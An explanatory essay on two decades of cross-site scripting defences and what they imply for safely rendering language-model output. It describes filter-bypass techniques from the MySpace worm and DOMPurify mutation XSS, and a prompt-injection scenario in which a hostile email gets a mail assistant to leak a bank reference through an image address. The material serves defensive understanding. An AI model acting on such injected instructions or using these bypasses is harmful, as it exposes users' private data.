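# What two decades of cross-site scripting defence predict about securing model outputs

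## How a browser turns text into action

Cross-site scripting (XSS) is an attack in which an attacker's text runs as code in another site's page, with that page's privileges. Microsoft security engineers coined the name in January 2000, when the typical attack involved one site loading another. OWASP, a non-profit community of security practitioners, now calls the name a misnomer in its *Cross Site Scripting Prevention Cheat Sheet*, because the term has widened to cover the injection of almost any content. The flaw remains common, and in 2025 MITRE, an American research organisation, again ranked it first in its list of the most dangerous software weaknesses.

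Over two decades, web developers defended against cross-site scripting first by filtering what users typed, then by encoding text when they output it, and then by sending browsers rules about which scripts may run. Programs built on large language models (LLMs) now have a closely related problem, because a chat window or mail assistant displays model-written text that an attacker can influence. How much of the web's experience applies to them depends first on what a browser does with a string of characters.

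### From characters to a page

A page reaches the browser as a string. A tokeniser splits the string into tags and text, and a tree builder assembles these into a tree of objects called the Document Object Model (DOM). For example, `<p>Hello world.` becomes a paragraph object containing the text "Hello world." The browser draws the page from this tree, and scripts in the page can read and change the tree.

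Content and commands share the same string, and only punctuation separates them. The rules are in WHATWG's *Parsing HTML documents*, part of the HTML standard that browser makers maintain. An angle bracket followed by a letter opens a tag, but one followed by a digit is plain text, so `<42>` appears on the screen as typed. The standard also specifies how the parser recovers from broken markup. For instance, the parser drops a repeated attribute and closes a comment that the author forgot to close. Almost any string therefore produces some page, and a filter that reads text by slightly different rules can approve one page while the browser builds another. WHATWG describes an older mismatch of this sort, in which validators followed the formal grammar of early HTML while browsers followed their own rules.

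Some objects in the tree trigger actions. A script element runs code, and an image element makes the browser request an address. Certain attributes hold event handlers, code that runs on a click or when an image fails to load. Security engineers use the term "sink" for a point where a program hands text to something that interprets it. The HTML parser and the URL loader are both sinks.

### What the same-origin policy protects

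The same-origin policy limits how one open site can interact with another. CS 161's *Same-Origin Policy*, a chapter of a university security textbook, gives the example of a malicious site open beside Gmail. Without the policy, the malicious site could read the user's mail or send mail in the user's name. *The Web Origin Concept* (Barth, 2011) defines an origin as the combination of scheme, host and port. Two pages at `https://example.com` share an origin whatever their paths, but a page at `http://example.com` has a different one. A script can work freely with objects from its own origin but, with a few exceptions, cannot access those from another.

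There is no such barrier inside an origin. Barth explains that an image carries no authority, but an HTML document and every script in it carry the full authority of the document's origin. That includes scripts the page imports from other hosts. A script's privileges depend on the page it runs in, not on who wrote it. If an attacker's text becomes a script in the mail site's page, the same-origin policy gives it the same access as the mail site's own code, because nothing in the tree records that the text came from someone else. The script can then read what the user can read there and send requests as that user.

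The policy also generally stops a page from reading information from another origin, but lets it send information there. Barth explains that a browser that blocked all requests to other origins would stop people following links. A page may also display images from anywhere. Requesting an image sends the image's address to the server, and that address can contain a name or an account number. Exfiltration, which means sending private data to a destination the attacker controls, therefore does not always need a script.

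### Stored, reflected and DOM-based XSS

A bold tag is a harmless test for all three kinds of XSS. If a visitor types `<b>` around a word and the word appears in bold, the site has passed the visitor's text to the HTML parser as markup, and other tags may get through.

In stored XSS, the site saves the text and shows it to other people later. In *Securing the Tangled Web*, Google's Kern imagines a photo-sharing service that notifies users when somebody invites them to view an album. Suppose a member names an album `<b>Lisbon</b>`. The server saves the title, and the invited friend sees a notification with "Lisbon" in bold.

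In reflected XSS, a site repeats text from a request in its response without saving it. For example, a visitor searches a shop for `<b>tea</b>`, and the results page shows the query with "tea" in bold. An attacker would put malicious markup into a link to the shop and persuade somebody to follow it.

In DOM-based XSS, the mistake is in the page's own script. For example, a script might greet visitors by a name it takes from the part of the address after the `#` sign. It decodes the name and assigns it to `innerHTML`, a property that parses a string as HTML and puts the result into the page. A link ending in `#<b>Ana</b>` then makes the name appear in bold. Browsers do not send that part of the address to the server, so a filter there cannot check it. Kotowicz, in *Prevent DOM-based cross-site scripting vulnerabilities with Trusted Types*, describes the pattern as data travelling from a source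 that a user controls to a sink that can execute code.

### One comment, three treatments

Suppose somebody posts the comment `I <3 <b>tea</b>` on a site. The first angle bracket is half of a heart and the others are markup. Validation checks the comment against a rule and accepts or refuses it. Sanitisation removes the dangerous parts of the markup and keeps the rest. Output encoding rewrites characters on output so the parser treats them as plain data.

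| Treatment | What the site puts in the page | What readers see |
|---|---|---|
| Validation, with a rule against angle brackets | Nothing | No comment; the writer gets an error message |
| Sanitisation, with bold text allowed | `I &lt;3 <b>tea</b>` | The heart, then "tea" in bold |
| Output encoding | `I &lt;3 &lt;b&gt;tea&lt;/b&gt;` | `I <3 <b>tea</b>`, exactly as typed |

All three are safe here, but they differ in what the writer loses. Validation rejects a harmless comment. It suits values with a narrow form, and it is necessary for web addresses. *Securing the Tangled Web* describes a login page that redirects users to an address it finds in the current URL. Some addresses contain code that runs when the browser opens them, so the page should check that the scheme is a benign one such as `https`. HTML encoding would not help, because the browser decodes the characters before it uses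 the address.

Encoding is the right default for text that should appear as typed, provided the encoder matches where the text will be inserted. Better still, a script can assign the text to `textContent`, which inserts it as text without calling the HTML parser.

Sanitisation is for sites whose users need formatting, and it is the most fragile of the three. OWASP warns that changing the string after sanitisation can undo the protection, and that sanitisers need regular patches because browsers change and researchers keep finding bypasses. The HTML standard now includes its own sanitiser. WHATWG's *Dynamic markup insertion* specifies `setHTML`, a method that cleans markup while the browser parses it, which should reduce differences between how a filter interprets the markup and what the browser builds from it. According to MDN's *Element* page on the method, `setHTML` always removes scripts,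 embedded frames and event handlers, even where a developer's settings would allow them, though some widely used browsers still lack it.

### From a model's reply to the screen

A model's reply is also a string. Chat products usually have the model write in Markdown, a notation in which asterisks mark bold text and brackets mark links and images. The renderer, the program that turns the model's text into what the user sees, then passes this text through several interpreters.

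1. A Markdown converter turns the reply into HTML. `**Two** invoices are due` becomes `<strong>Two</strong> invoices are due`. This is already a sink, since punctuation in the reply now decides which elements exist. Many converters can also pass along any HTML that the reply contains.
2. The page's script hands the HTML to the browser's parser, often through `innerHTML` or a framework's equivalent. This is the sink of classic XSS.
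3. The URL loader fetches the address of every image in the result. The user clicks nothing. Addresses in links reach the same sink later, if the user follows them.

Other products send the reply to a terminal, which has its own control sequences, or to a shell or database that runs it as a command.

Auth0's *Trusting AI Output?*, a tutorial from an identity-software company, walks through the second step. An assistant summarises a hostile web page, the summary contains a script element, and the application assigns the summary to `innerHTML`. The tutorial says the browser then runs the script, which is wrong. According to MDN's *Element* page on `innerHTML`, script elements inserted this way do not execute, but event handlers do. The application is therefore still vulnerable, and a developer who tested it with only a script element would wrongly conclude that the chat window was safe. The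 tutorial's fix, `textContent`, works but shows the user raw asterisks and brackets, so a product that displays headings and links in its replies still needs sanitisation.

OWASP's category for these failures, *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, covers insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of a model's output before other components receive it. Most of the remedies it lists are familiar, including encoding for the destination and a strict Content Security Policy (rules, sent with a page, about which scripts may run and where resources may come from). It also advises developers to treat the model like any other user. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026), a survey that matches LLM risks to MITRE's catalogue of software weaknesses, similarly places improper output handling under old entries, including the failure to encode output properly.

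### Prompt injection and the hostile email

A model's reply can be unsafe even when the user and the developer are both honest, because the model may also read text from a third party. Prompt injection is text in that material that makes the model follow an attacker's instructions. It works because the developer's instructions, the user's request and the material all reach the model as text, and current models do not reliably distinguish what they should obey from what they should only read.

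An email assistant might run in a panel inside the mail site's own page, which gives it the mail site's origin. An office worker asks it to summarise twelve new emails. Eleven are ordinary, including one that contains the reference number of a bank transfer. The twelfth, from a stranger, contains a sales offer followed by a paragraph addressed to any AI system reading the mail. In that paragraph, the stranger asks for the summary to end with an image from the stranger's server and for the image's address to include the reference number.

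The stranger's words can reach the panel in two ways. The model may follow the instructions in the paragraph, or it may simply quote the email, as a good summary sometimes should, and include its markup. The second can happen even if the model resists every injected instruction.

What happens next depends on the renderer. If the panel accepts any HTML, the stranger can try to run code with the mail site's privileges, which is ordinary stored XSS delivered through a model. If it removes scripts but loads images, the browser sends the reference number out in an image request. If it shows plain text, the browser fetches nothing, but the summary could still include an instruction to call a false number for the bank. Willison (2026) describes a similar image-based flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent that could send messages to its user's own inbox without approval. The inbox displayed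 those messages in a way that could leak data through images.

OWASP's 2026 list of LLM risks ranks the two halves of this example far apart, with prompt injection first and improper output handling tenth and last. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a security vendor's reading of the list, a vote among practitioners made up three quarters of the weighting. The rest came from 7,714 recorded incidents, of which 6,639 were detailed enough to classify. On the incidents alone, prompt injection would have dropped out of the top ten. OWASP's explanation is that defenders work hard on prompt injection, so fewer clean exploits reach the public databases. That is plausible, but the count would also be low if those databases were simply better at recording flaws in code than manipulated models. Improper output handling fell from fifth place as other risks rose, while its scope grew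 to include terminals and renderers that fetch external resources on their own, so its lower rank doesn't mean that output handling has become safer.

Invicti also quotes the list's advice to developers: "Stop trying to build a model that cannot be fooled." They should instead build the surrounding system so that a fooled model breaks nothing important. For the mailbox, much of that protection depends on the renderer, where the web's experience might help.

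The mailbox differs from the photo-sharing service in one large way, because a model writes the text that the page displays. The photo-sharing page displayed the attacker's text directly, and a reviewer could in principle trace an album title from the form where somebody typed it to the sink where it did harm. In the mailbox, all twelve emails may have shaped any sentence of the summary, and the stranger's request can appear in words the stranger never used, so no reviewer can mark which characters came from whom. This doesn't affect an encoder, which treats every character alike wherever it came from. It makes a filter that searches incoming mail for dangerous strings much less effective, since a request in ordinary English need not contain any. Most of the web's other defences are affected more than the encoder but less than the filter, and the question is which of them still work when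 the attacker can only influence the model that writes the output.

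## MySpace, 2005: filtering dangerous input

Filtering is the oldest of the web's defences, and its best-known failure happened on MySpace, then the world's most popular social network. Members could decorate their profiles with HTML, so MySpace could not encode everything they typed. Instead, it filtered their text, removing whatever its developers considered dangerous. In October 2005 Samy Kamkar, a 19-year-old in Los Angeles, wrote code that got through the filter and copied itself into the profile of every logged-in member who viewed an infected profile.

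### What the filter missed

Kamkar published *Technical explanation of The MySpace Worm* after MySpace closed the hole. By this account, the filter seemed to allow only links, images, `div` blocks (plain containers) and perhaps a few other elements. It removed script elements, event handlers and links with JavaScript in the address. It also deleted certain words wherever they appeared, including "javascript". Kamkar found a way around the assumption behind each rule.

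| What the filter did | The assumption | Why it failed |
|---|---|---|
| Allowed style rules on a `div` | Styles affect only appearance | Internet Explorer and some versions of Safari also ran code from an address inside a style rule |
| Deleted the word "javascript" | The word works only if it is unbroken | Some browsers ignored a line break in the middle of it |
| Deleted escaped quotation marks | Code that needs a quotation mark must contain one | The code produced the character from its number as it ran |
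| Deleted the names of certain browser features | Code that uses a feature must contain its name | The code joined the name together from two halves as it ran |

A better-informed developer could have closed the gaps involving styles and line breaks. The assembled names are a harder problem, because a program can build any word as it runs, and a search through the program's text will not find a word built that way. More generally, the filter and the browser interpreted the same text by different rules. MySpace's developers had to anticipate every interpretation by every browser their members used, including some that no standard described, because Kamkar could exploit any one they missed.

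Once the code ran, it had the privileges of MySpace's own pages. It read the viewer's member number from the page and fetched the viewer's list of personal heroes. It then tried to submit the form for adding a friend, but the form was on `www.myspace.com` and the code was running on `profile.myspace.com`, so the browser blocked the request. MySpace served the same profiles at both addresses, so the code reloaded the page at `www.myspace.com`. The form also required a random value from a confirmation page, a common defence against requests forged by other sites. The code fetched that page, read the value and sent it back. Finally, it copied its own source into the viewer's list of heroes, along with the words "but most of all, samy is my hero", so the next member to open that profile ran the code too.

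Kamkar released the worm just after midnight on 4 October. In an interview quoted in Computerworld's *Teen uses worm to boost popularity* (2005), he recalled 200 friend requests after eight hours, 2,000 a few hours later, then 200,000, then a million. Writers Write's *Teen Hacks His Way to MySpace Popularity* reports that he reached a million in under 20 hours. MySpace did not comment, so the count is Kamkar's own. *Cross-Site Scripting Worms & Viruses* (Grossman, 2007) also reports over a million profiles, perhaps from the same count, and adds that MySpace had to shut down its site to clean up.

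Grossman, whose company sold website security, compared the spread of Kamkar's worm with that of earlier worms. In their first 24 hours, Code Red infected 359,000 computers and Blaster 336,000. Those worms took over whole machines, while Kamkar's affected only MySpace accounts, so the comparison is about speed, not damage. According to Grossman, the older worms spread more slowly because they tried internet addresses at random and clogged the network with useless traffic, whereas Kamkar's code ran when someone visited an infected profile, so each visitor was a possible victim.

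### What CERT had recommended in 2000

The CERT Coordination Center (2000), a security response centre at Carnegie Mellon University, had described the flaw in an advisory more than five years earlier. It warned that removing dangerous characters from input "leaves a number of risks unaddressed". It advised developers instead to accept only characters they had explicitly allowed, and to check the text while generating the page. CERT had received no reports of malicious use. Slemko's *Re: recent 'cross site scripting' CERT advisory* (2000), a post on the Bugtraq security mailing list, quotes Tim Hollebeek, who called it a misconception that hackers had never exploited the problem and pointed to Microsoft's Hotmail. He also wrote that security experts had known of such flaws for a long time.

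CERT Coordination Center's companion document, *Understanding Malicious Content Mitigation for Web Developers*, gives the reasons for the advice. Different characters have special meanings in different parts of a page. Browsers try to repair bad HTML, so they sometimes give a character a special meaning that the standard does not. If a server doesn't declare its character set, developers can't predict which bytes the browser will treat as an angle bracket. Text can also enter a site's database without passing through a web form, and a filter on the form doesn't check that text.

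MySpace's filter ignored much of this advice, but the advice was also incomplete. CERT's example of an allowlist was a form field for a person's age, which needs only digits. A profile with bold text and pictures needs angle brackets, and encoding them would have displayed the tags as text instead of applying the formatting. CERT also described encoding as resource-intensive and told developers to balance it against filtering. Three of the document's four sample filter functions delete a list of bad characters, although the text recommends allowing only characters known to be safe. A developer who copied an example would probably have ended up with a blocklist.

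### Magic quotes: escaping before the destination is known

PHP, the programming language behind many early websites, had a feature called magic quotes that was meant to make input safe automatically. It put a backslash before every quotation mark, backslash and null character that arrived in a web address, form or cookie. It was on by default, according to *What are Magic Quotes*, a page of the PHP manual. It was meant to stop SQL injection, an attack in which a quotation mark in a form field ends a piece of text inside a database command, so that the database treats whatever follows as part of the command.

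PHP added the backslashes before it knew where the text would go. thePHP.cc's *Why Magic Quotes are gone in PHP 7* explains that each destination has its own dangerous characters. In a database command, the quotation mark is dangerous, though the SQL standard escapes it by doubling it, not with a backslash. In HTML, angle brackets are dangerous, but magic quotes didn't escape them. The comment `I <3 <b>tea</b>` contains no quotation marks, so it would have passed through unchanged and appeared with "tea" in bold. A shop's email to a customer called O'Brien, on the other hand, might have begun "Dear O\\'Brien".

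Server administrators could switch off PHP's magic quotes feature, so a program could not rely on it. A careful developer had to check the setting, undo any escaping, and then escape the text again for its real destination. Olson (2008), in *Request for Comments*, proposed phasing the feature out, and wrote that all the participants agreed it was not the best solution to any problem, but that people used it anyway. The main worry was that PHP would suddenly turn off something that had been on by default, which would call for "an extremely strong education effort". PHP removed magic quotes in version 5.4, in 2012.

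### Filters inside the browser

Microsoft and Google tried to catch attacks in the browser, which could protect people on sites that never fixed their flaws. Both concentrated on reflected XSS, in which the same markup appears in the request and the response, so the browser can compare the two.

Microsoft introduced its filter with Internet Explorer 8 in 2008. The filter searched each request for patterns that resembled script, and if a match came back in the page, it altered the page's text to disable the script. It did this before the browser parsed the page, so it had to approximate what the parser would do. Bates, Barth and Jackson (2010), in *Regular Expressions Considered Harmful in Client-Side XSS Filters*, showed that the filter therefore flagged script tags inside a text box, where browsers treat them as plain text, and missed scripts written in UTF-7, a character encoding that CERT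 had warned about ten years earlier.

Bates and colleagues moved the filter to run after the parser. Google adopted their design in Chrome as the XSS Auditor, which checked each script against the request after the parser identified it and before it ran. The researchers examined 145 publicly reported flaws and judged 96.5% to be within the filter's scope, meaning they had designed it to block every way of injecting a script through those flaws. That figure describes the filter's intended coverage, not its success against attackers trying to get round it.

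A later test was less favourable. For *Precise client-side protection against DOM-based Cross-Site Scripting*, Stock, Lekies and colleagues built a system that automatically generated attacks for 1,602 real DOM-based flaws. The attacks got past the Auditor in 73% of cases. The test was somewhat unfair, since Google had aimed the Auditor at reflected XSS and had turned it off for `innerHTML` because it slowed some pages down. But some of the bypasses exploited the way the Auditor compared text. For example, it did nothing unless the request contained an angle bracket or a quotation mark, and some vulnerable pages could be attacked without either.

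The filters also harmed sites that had no flaw. When the same script appears in a request and a page, the browser cannot determine whether the site copied it from the request or already had it. An attacker could put a site's own script tag into a link, and the filter would disable that script for anyone who followed the link. Bates and colleagues used a similar trick on Facebook, which relied on a style sheet to keep other companies' gadgets inside a small rectangle. They made Microsoft's filter disable the style sheet, which allowed a gadget to show a fake login page on Facebook's own address.

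According to The Chromium Projects' *XSS Auditor*, Chrome responded to this kind of abuse in version 57 by blocking the whole page instead of removing one script. But blocking let a malicious site work out the content of other sites' pages, which the same-origin policy should have prevented. The malicious site could load someone else's page in a frame, include a guess at some of its script in the request, and see whether the browser blocked the page. If it did, the guess was right, and the site could repeat the process to learn more.

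Microsoft removed the filter from Edge, Internet Explorer's successor, in October 2018. Lawrence (2018) explains in *An Update on the Edge XSS Filter* that a rewrite of Edge's download code had accidentally reversed the filter's logic, so it checked navigation within a site and ignored navigation between sites, where it was supposed to work. While handling the bug reports, Microsoft's engineers concluded that the filter's drawbacks had long outweighed its benefits.

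Google followed in 2019. Sepez (2019), in *Intent to Deprecate and Remove*, gave five reasons: "Bypasses abound," the Auditor broke some legitimate sites, it leaked information between sites, the leaks had proved difficult to fix, and "Once detected, there's nothing good to do." The last reason would apply even to a filter that nobody could bypass. If the Auditor removed a suspicious script, attackers could choose which scripts to disable, and if it blocked the page, they could learn what the page contained.

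### Sanitisers that use a parser

None of this helped a site like MySpace, whose members wanted bold text and pictures. A modern sanitiser can allow them fairly safely because it works on the parsed tree rather than the raw text.

DOMPurify, an open-source library from the German security company Cure53, is the best-known example. It gives the markup to the browser's parser, which builds a tree in a separate document where scripts do not run. The library then removes every element and attribute that is not on an allowlist. Because a new event handler would not be on the list, the library would remove it without having to detect an attack. By default, DOMPurify then turns the cleaned tree back into a string.

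That last step is the weak point. Developers typically get a clean string from DOMPurify in one line of code and assign it to `innerHTML` in the next, as Braun shows in *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()*. The browser then parses the markup a second time, and the second tree can differ from the one that DOMPurify checked. Security researchers call attacks that exploit this difference mutation XSS.

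Nested forms show how such a difference arises. The parser normally doesn't put one form inside another, but certain badly nested tags make it do so. If a program writes that tree out as a string and parses it again, the inner form disappears and nearby elements can move. In 2020 the security researcher Michał Bentkowski used this to get past DOMPurify. On the second parse, an element moved into a mathematical formula, where the parser follows different rules, and harmless text turned into live markup. Cure53 fixed the problem in version 2.0.17, but researchers have found other bypasses since.

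Cure53 fixed one of these in DOMPurify, CVE-2025-26791, in February 2025. It affected an optional mode that removes template code, the placeholders that some frameworks fill in or execute. Although DOMPurify is built on a parser, this mode looked for template code with a text pattern, and an error in that pattern caused the flaw.

The Sanitizer API, the browser feature behind `setHTML`, eliminates the second parse. The browser parses the markup once, removes disallowed content, and inserts the resulting tree directly into the page. It also takes into account which element will receive the markup, because the same tags can produce different trees in different places. For example, the parser accepts a table cell's tag inside a table row but ignores it in a paragraph. The guide *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* on web.dev, Google's site for web developers, presents both as improvements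 on DOMPurify's approach. Alfy (2026) adds that a sanitiser inside the browser by definition stays consistent with the parser, whereas a library's maintainers have to keep up with every browser release.

A page can still lose this protection if it later reads the cleaned content back as a string and assigns it to `innerHTML` elsewhere, because the browser then parses it again. `setHTML` guarantees only that the markup cannot run scripts. If a developer's settings allow images, the browser will still request them, sending whatever information their addresses contain.

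Browser support for the Sanitizer API is recent and incomplete. According to Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML*, Firefox 148 was the first browser to ship the standard version. Web Platform DX's catalogue entry, *Sanitizer API*, dates that release to 24 February 2026. Chrome and Edge have supported the API since version 146 according to web.dev, but the catalogue marks both as unsupported, possibly because its entry is older. Neither source lists support in Safari, so most sites will need to keep a library such as DOMPurify for some time.

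### Filters on a model's input and output

A developer could try to protect the mailbox assistant by filtering either the emails the model reads or the summary it writes. The web's experience suggests that filtering the summary is much more likely to work, provided the filter runs on the parsed summary.

A filter on the emails would have to recognise the stranger's paragraph as an attack before the model read it. Microsoft had a similar problem when it tried to predict what a browser would do with a page, but a browser has a parser, and Google could move its filter to run after the parser. A language model has no comparable set of rules. It may follow a request in French, or one full of spelling mistakes, or one spread across several polite sentences, and no list of phrases could cover them all. A trained classifier should do better, since it can recognise wordings that nobody listed. But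 it still interprets the email separately from the model it protects, and an attacker can keep trying different wordings until the classifier passes one that the model follows.

Lawrence points out that bypasses of the browser filters stayed usable for a long time because updates were slow, taking about six weeks for Chrome and at least several months for Internet Explorer. Companies that host their own models have an advantage here because they can change their filters the same day. Faster updates would help against known attacks, though attackers could still test new ones in private before using them.

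The filter would also flag some legitimate emails, because many contain instructions, such as a request to forward an invoice, and a security newsletter might quote a prompt injection to explain it. If the assistant dropped every suspicious message, a stranger could perhaps hide a genuine conversation from the summary by replying to it with a phrase that triggers the filter. Attackers exploited the same weakness in the XSS Auditor to disable a site's own scripts.

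On the output side, a filter that searches the summary for the usual Markdown image notation would repeat MySpace's mistake, because Markdown has more than one way to write an image. Researchers later exploited this gap in Microsoft 365 Copilot. It would be safer to apply an allowlist to the tree after the converter and the HTML parser have run. By then every image is an image element, however the model wrote it, and the wording of the stranger's request no longer matters. The false phone number for the bank would still get through, because it is ordinary text.

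## Google's templates: encoding output for its context

Google's page templates encode each value when they output it, using the rule for its exact position in the page, whereas PHP's magic quotes escaped text before its destination was known. With some additions, Google's approach brought XSS in its newer applications close to zero, which is probably the web's greatest success against the problem. But it requires a developer to have written the page's markup in advance, and in a chat product the model often writes much of the markup.

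### One string in five places

Suppose a member of the photo-sharing service names an album `tea: <b>"Earl's"</b>; hot`. The title is harmless, but some of its characters have special meanings in different parts of a page. A value's output context is the syntactic position where it is inserted. The simplest HTML encoder rewrites only ampersands and angle brackets, which is enough for only one of these five contexts.

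| Where the title lands | What goes wrong with the simplest encoder | A correct result |
|---|---|---|
| HTML text | Nothing | `tea: &lt;b&gt;"Earl's"&lt;/b&gt;; hot` |
| A quoted attribute, such as an image's description | The first quotation mark ends the attribute, and the browser reads the rest as further attributes, which could include event handlers | `tea: &lt;b&gt;&quot;Earl&#39;s&quot;&lt;/b&gt;; hot` |
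| A link's address | The browser reads `tea` as the scheme, and a different scheme could make it run the rest as code | No link, because `tea` is not a permitted scheme |
| A string in a script | A quotation mark ends the string, and the rest becomes part of the program | `tea: \x3cb\x3e\x22Earl\x27s\x22\x3c/b\x3e; hot` |
| A style value, such as a colour | A semicolon ends the colour, and the browser reads what follows as another style instruction | No colour, because the title doesn't look like one |

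An HTML encoder that also rewrites quotation marks would protect the attribute. It wouldn't protect the link, because the dangerous part of the address consists of letters and a colon, which it wouldn't change. The browser doesn't decode HTML's codes inside a script element, so the script would receive `&quot;Earl&#39;s&quot;` instead of the real title. A title ending in a backslash could still cancel the string's closing quotation mark. In an event handler, the browser decodes the codes before it passes the text to the script engine, so the decoded apostrophe would end the string. Encoding for a script wouldn't suit HTML text either, because readers would see `\x3cb\x3e` on the screen.

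Contexts can also be nested. A link's address is usually inside a quoted attribute, so it needs a scheme check and then attribute encoding. Samuel, Palmer and colleagues (2026) give a three-language example in *Compile-time Security Analysis and Optimization of Sensitive String Producers*. In it, an HTML attribute contains a style instruction that contains the address of a background image. The address needs quotation marks to be safe in the style language, and those marks then need HTML encoding so that they don't end the attribute.

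Developers who choose encoders by hand make mistakes even in serious products. In *SCRIPTGARD*, Saxena, Molnar and Livshits analysed a commercial web application with over 400,000 lines of code and found sanitisers that didn't suit the browser context and others that developers had combined inconsistently. Such mistakes are hard to spot. As *DjangoChecker* (2020) points out, an application with the wrong sanitiser looks protected but can be as vulnerable as one with none.

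### How a template engine chooses the encoder

In a template, the developer writes the fixed markup and the program fills the gaps with values such as names and titles. In 2011, Samuel, Saxena and Song showed in *Context-Sensitive Auto-Sanitization in Web Templating Languages Using Type Qualifiers* how a compiler could choose the right encoder for every gap, a method now called contextual auto-escaping. They built it into Closure Templates, the system behind Gmail and Google Docs.

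The photo-sharing service might use this template, with gaps in curly brackets:

```
<a href="/search?q={title}">{title}</a>
<a href="{blog}">Owner's blog</a>
```

The engine reads the fixed text from left to right and keeps track of the state that a browser's parser would be in.

1. It starts in HTML text. After `<a href="` the browser would be at the start of an address, inside a quoted attribute.
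2. After `/search?q=` the browser would be in the query, the part of an address that holds search terms. The first gap is here, so the engine inserts an encoder that turns special characters into percent codes. The album title becomes `tea%3A%20%3Cb%3E%22Earl%27s%22%3C%2Fb%3E%3B%20hot`.
3. The characters `">` close the attribute and the tag. The next gap is in HTML text, so the same title now gets HTML encoding.
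4. The second link opens, and its gap comes at the very start of the address. Here the value can choose the scheme, so the engine inserts a scheme check followed by an attribute encoder.
5. The remaining text closes the link. The engine ends in HTML text, so the program can safely insert the finished markup wherever HTML text belongs.

All of this happens when the developer compiles the template. When someone visits the page, the program only has to run the chosen encoders.

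Samuel, Saxena and Song expressed the method as a type system, a set of rules that a compiler uses to accept or reject a program. Every fixed string has a type *c*₁ → *c*₂, which means that a browser that starts reading it in context *c*₁ finishes in *c*₂. For example, the string `<a href="` leads from HTML text to the start of an address. An untrusted value has the type UNSAFE until it passes through an encoder for a particular context. If the page so far ends in context *c*₁, the program may add only a string of type *c*₁ → *c*₂, and the page then ends in *c*₂. The engine inserts an encoder wherever a template would otherwise break this rule. It does not encode the developer's own strings, since that would damage the page, and it rejects a template that puts a value where no known encoder can make it safe.

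Conditions and loops make it harder to choose the right encoder. In one of the researchers' examples, a contact card displays an image. If the contact has a name, the untrusted value goes into the query string of a URL on the site. If not, the value is the whole URL. The engine has to follow both branches and use a different encoder in each. Sometimes two branches leave the page in different contexts, so no single encoder is certain to be right for the next value, and the design postpones the choice until the program runs.

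Samuel and colleagues tested the engine on 1,035 templates from Google's applications. They switched off the encoders that developers had chosen by hand and had the engine choose replacements. It found an encoder for all 1,348 places where the templates output an untrusted value, and only nine had an ambiguous context. Plain HTML encoding, which frameworks such as Django applied everywhere at the time, would have been adequate in 982 of those places, or 72%.

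The perfect score shows only that the engine matched each encoder to its context, because the researchers assumed that every encoder was correct. A more informative result is that the engine agreed with the developers' own choices in all but 21 places, where the developers had used a stricter encoder than necessary. The engine exposed no new holes, because Google had already audited these templates, but it reproduced in 1.3 seconds what people had done carefully by hand. In three browsers, the encoders slowed the templates by 3% to 10%, whereas working out every context at run time slowed them by 79% to 425%.

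The method assumes that all major browsers parse the fixed markup in the same way, and that the rest of the program puts the result where HTML belongs. In 2026, Samuel and colleagues wrote that a good engine should guarantee what they call structure preservation, meaning that the fixed text adds the same structure to the parsed page whatever values fill the gaps. Even an empty value can break this if a developer omits the quotation marks around an attribute's value, because the browser then takes the next attribute's name as the value. Their engine therefore adds the missing quotation marks.

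A framework that handles only some contexts can leave a security gap for years. React, Meta's library for building interfaces, has HTML-like syntax but left developers to handle link addresses themselves. According to the same paper, React began to warn about addresses containing code in 2019 but did not fully block them until version 19.

### Strict templates and security types

A template engine protects only the markup that passes through it. Some code builds HTML without a template and assigns it to `innerHTML`, and some developers switch off the encoding for a value that needs formatting. Kern's *Securing the Tangled Web* (2014) addresses both problems.

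Members of Kern's imaginary photo-sharing service can use fonts, colours and links in their profiles, so the developer turns off encoding for the profile field. Members write the text in an editor that runs in their browser, and the developer expects it to produce only harmless markup. But an attacker can send text to the server without using the editor, and the server doesn't check it. Kern suggests that such a bug could arise when front-end and back-end developers misunderstand who is responsible for sanitising the text.

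In a strict template, nobody can turn the encoding off, and a strict template can include only other strict templates. A field that needs formatting must instead have a special type, a label that the compiler checks. Kern gives three examples:

- A value of type `SafeHtml` will not run an attacker's script when the page uses it as HTML.
- A value of type `SafeUrl` will not run an attacker's script when someone follows it as a link.
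- A value of type `TrustedResourceUrl` is the address of a script or style sheet that is itself trustworthy.

In general, a program cannot tell from a string alone whether it should have one of these labels, because that may depend on where the string came from and how it was processed. Google therefore lets only a few functions create labelled values. In the profile example, a sanitiser on the server cleans the text and labels the result `SafeHtml`. To attach the label, it calls an "unchecked conversion", a function that accepts any string without checking it. A security engineer must review every use of that function.

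The label stays attached to the text from the server to the page, where the template engine leaves the formatting intact only if the label applies in that context. If a developer puts a `SafeHtml` value into an attribute, the engine still encodes it, because a quotation mark in the value could end the attribute.

Finally, Google's compilers reject code that uses `innerHTML` and similar sinks directly, and the error message directs the developer to a safe alternative. Kern considers this automatic check necessary even in medium-sized projects, because violations creep in without it.

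Before these rules, a reviewer who wanted to show that an application had no XSS had to trace each value from its sink back to its origin, often through a database and other teams' code. A large application has hundreds or thousands of such paths. Under Kern's rules, every plain string counts as untrusted, even if it is harmless, so its origin no longer matters. The reviewer can concentrate on the template engine, the sanitiser and the few other places that create labelled values.

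### Checks in the compiler and the browser

Google first applied these rules to selected projects. In early 2018 it made the checks mandatory for all its JavaScript, the language used for scripts in web pages. *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile*, a 2021 study by Wang, Bangert and Kern, describes the result, which they call API hardening.

Google went through the HTML and DOM specifications by hand and listed every operation, or sink, that could make a browser run a string as code. These sinks execute code, follow links, load resources, parse HTML or apply styles. Styles no longer run code in modern browsers, but researchers had shown that an attacker's styles could reveal a page's text by making some of it slow to draw. Google therefore banned those sinks too.

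By design, the checker rejects every direct use of a listed sink without analysing whether the value is dangerous, so it is fast enough to run whenever a developer compiles. The developer must instead supply a labelled value, which can come from text typed into the program itself, a sanitiser, a strict template or a reviewed conversion.

A compiler can't enforce this completely, because JavaScript's type checkers have loopholes. A developer can disguise an object so that the compiler no longer recognises the sink. Wang and colleagues accept this, since such code looks strange and a reviewer should notice it.

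Trusted Types, a browser feature that grew out of this work, makes a similar check while the page runs. A site turns it on with a header, an instruction sent with the page. The browser then refuses plain strings at `innerHTML` and other dangerous sinks and accepts only special objects. Scripts can create these objects only through a policy, a small set of functions that the site's developers write. A policy for HTML would normally call a sanitiser.

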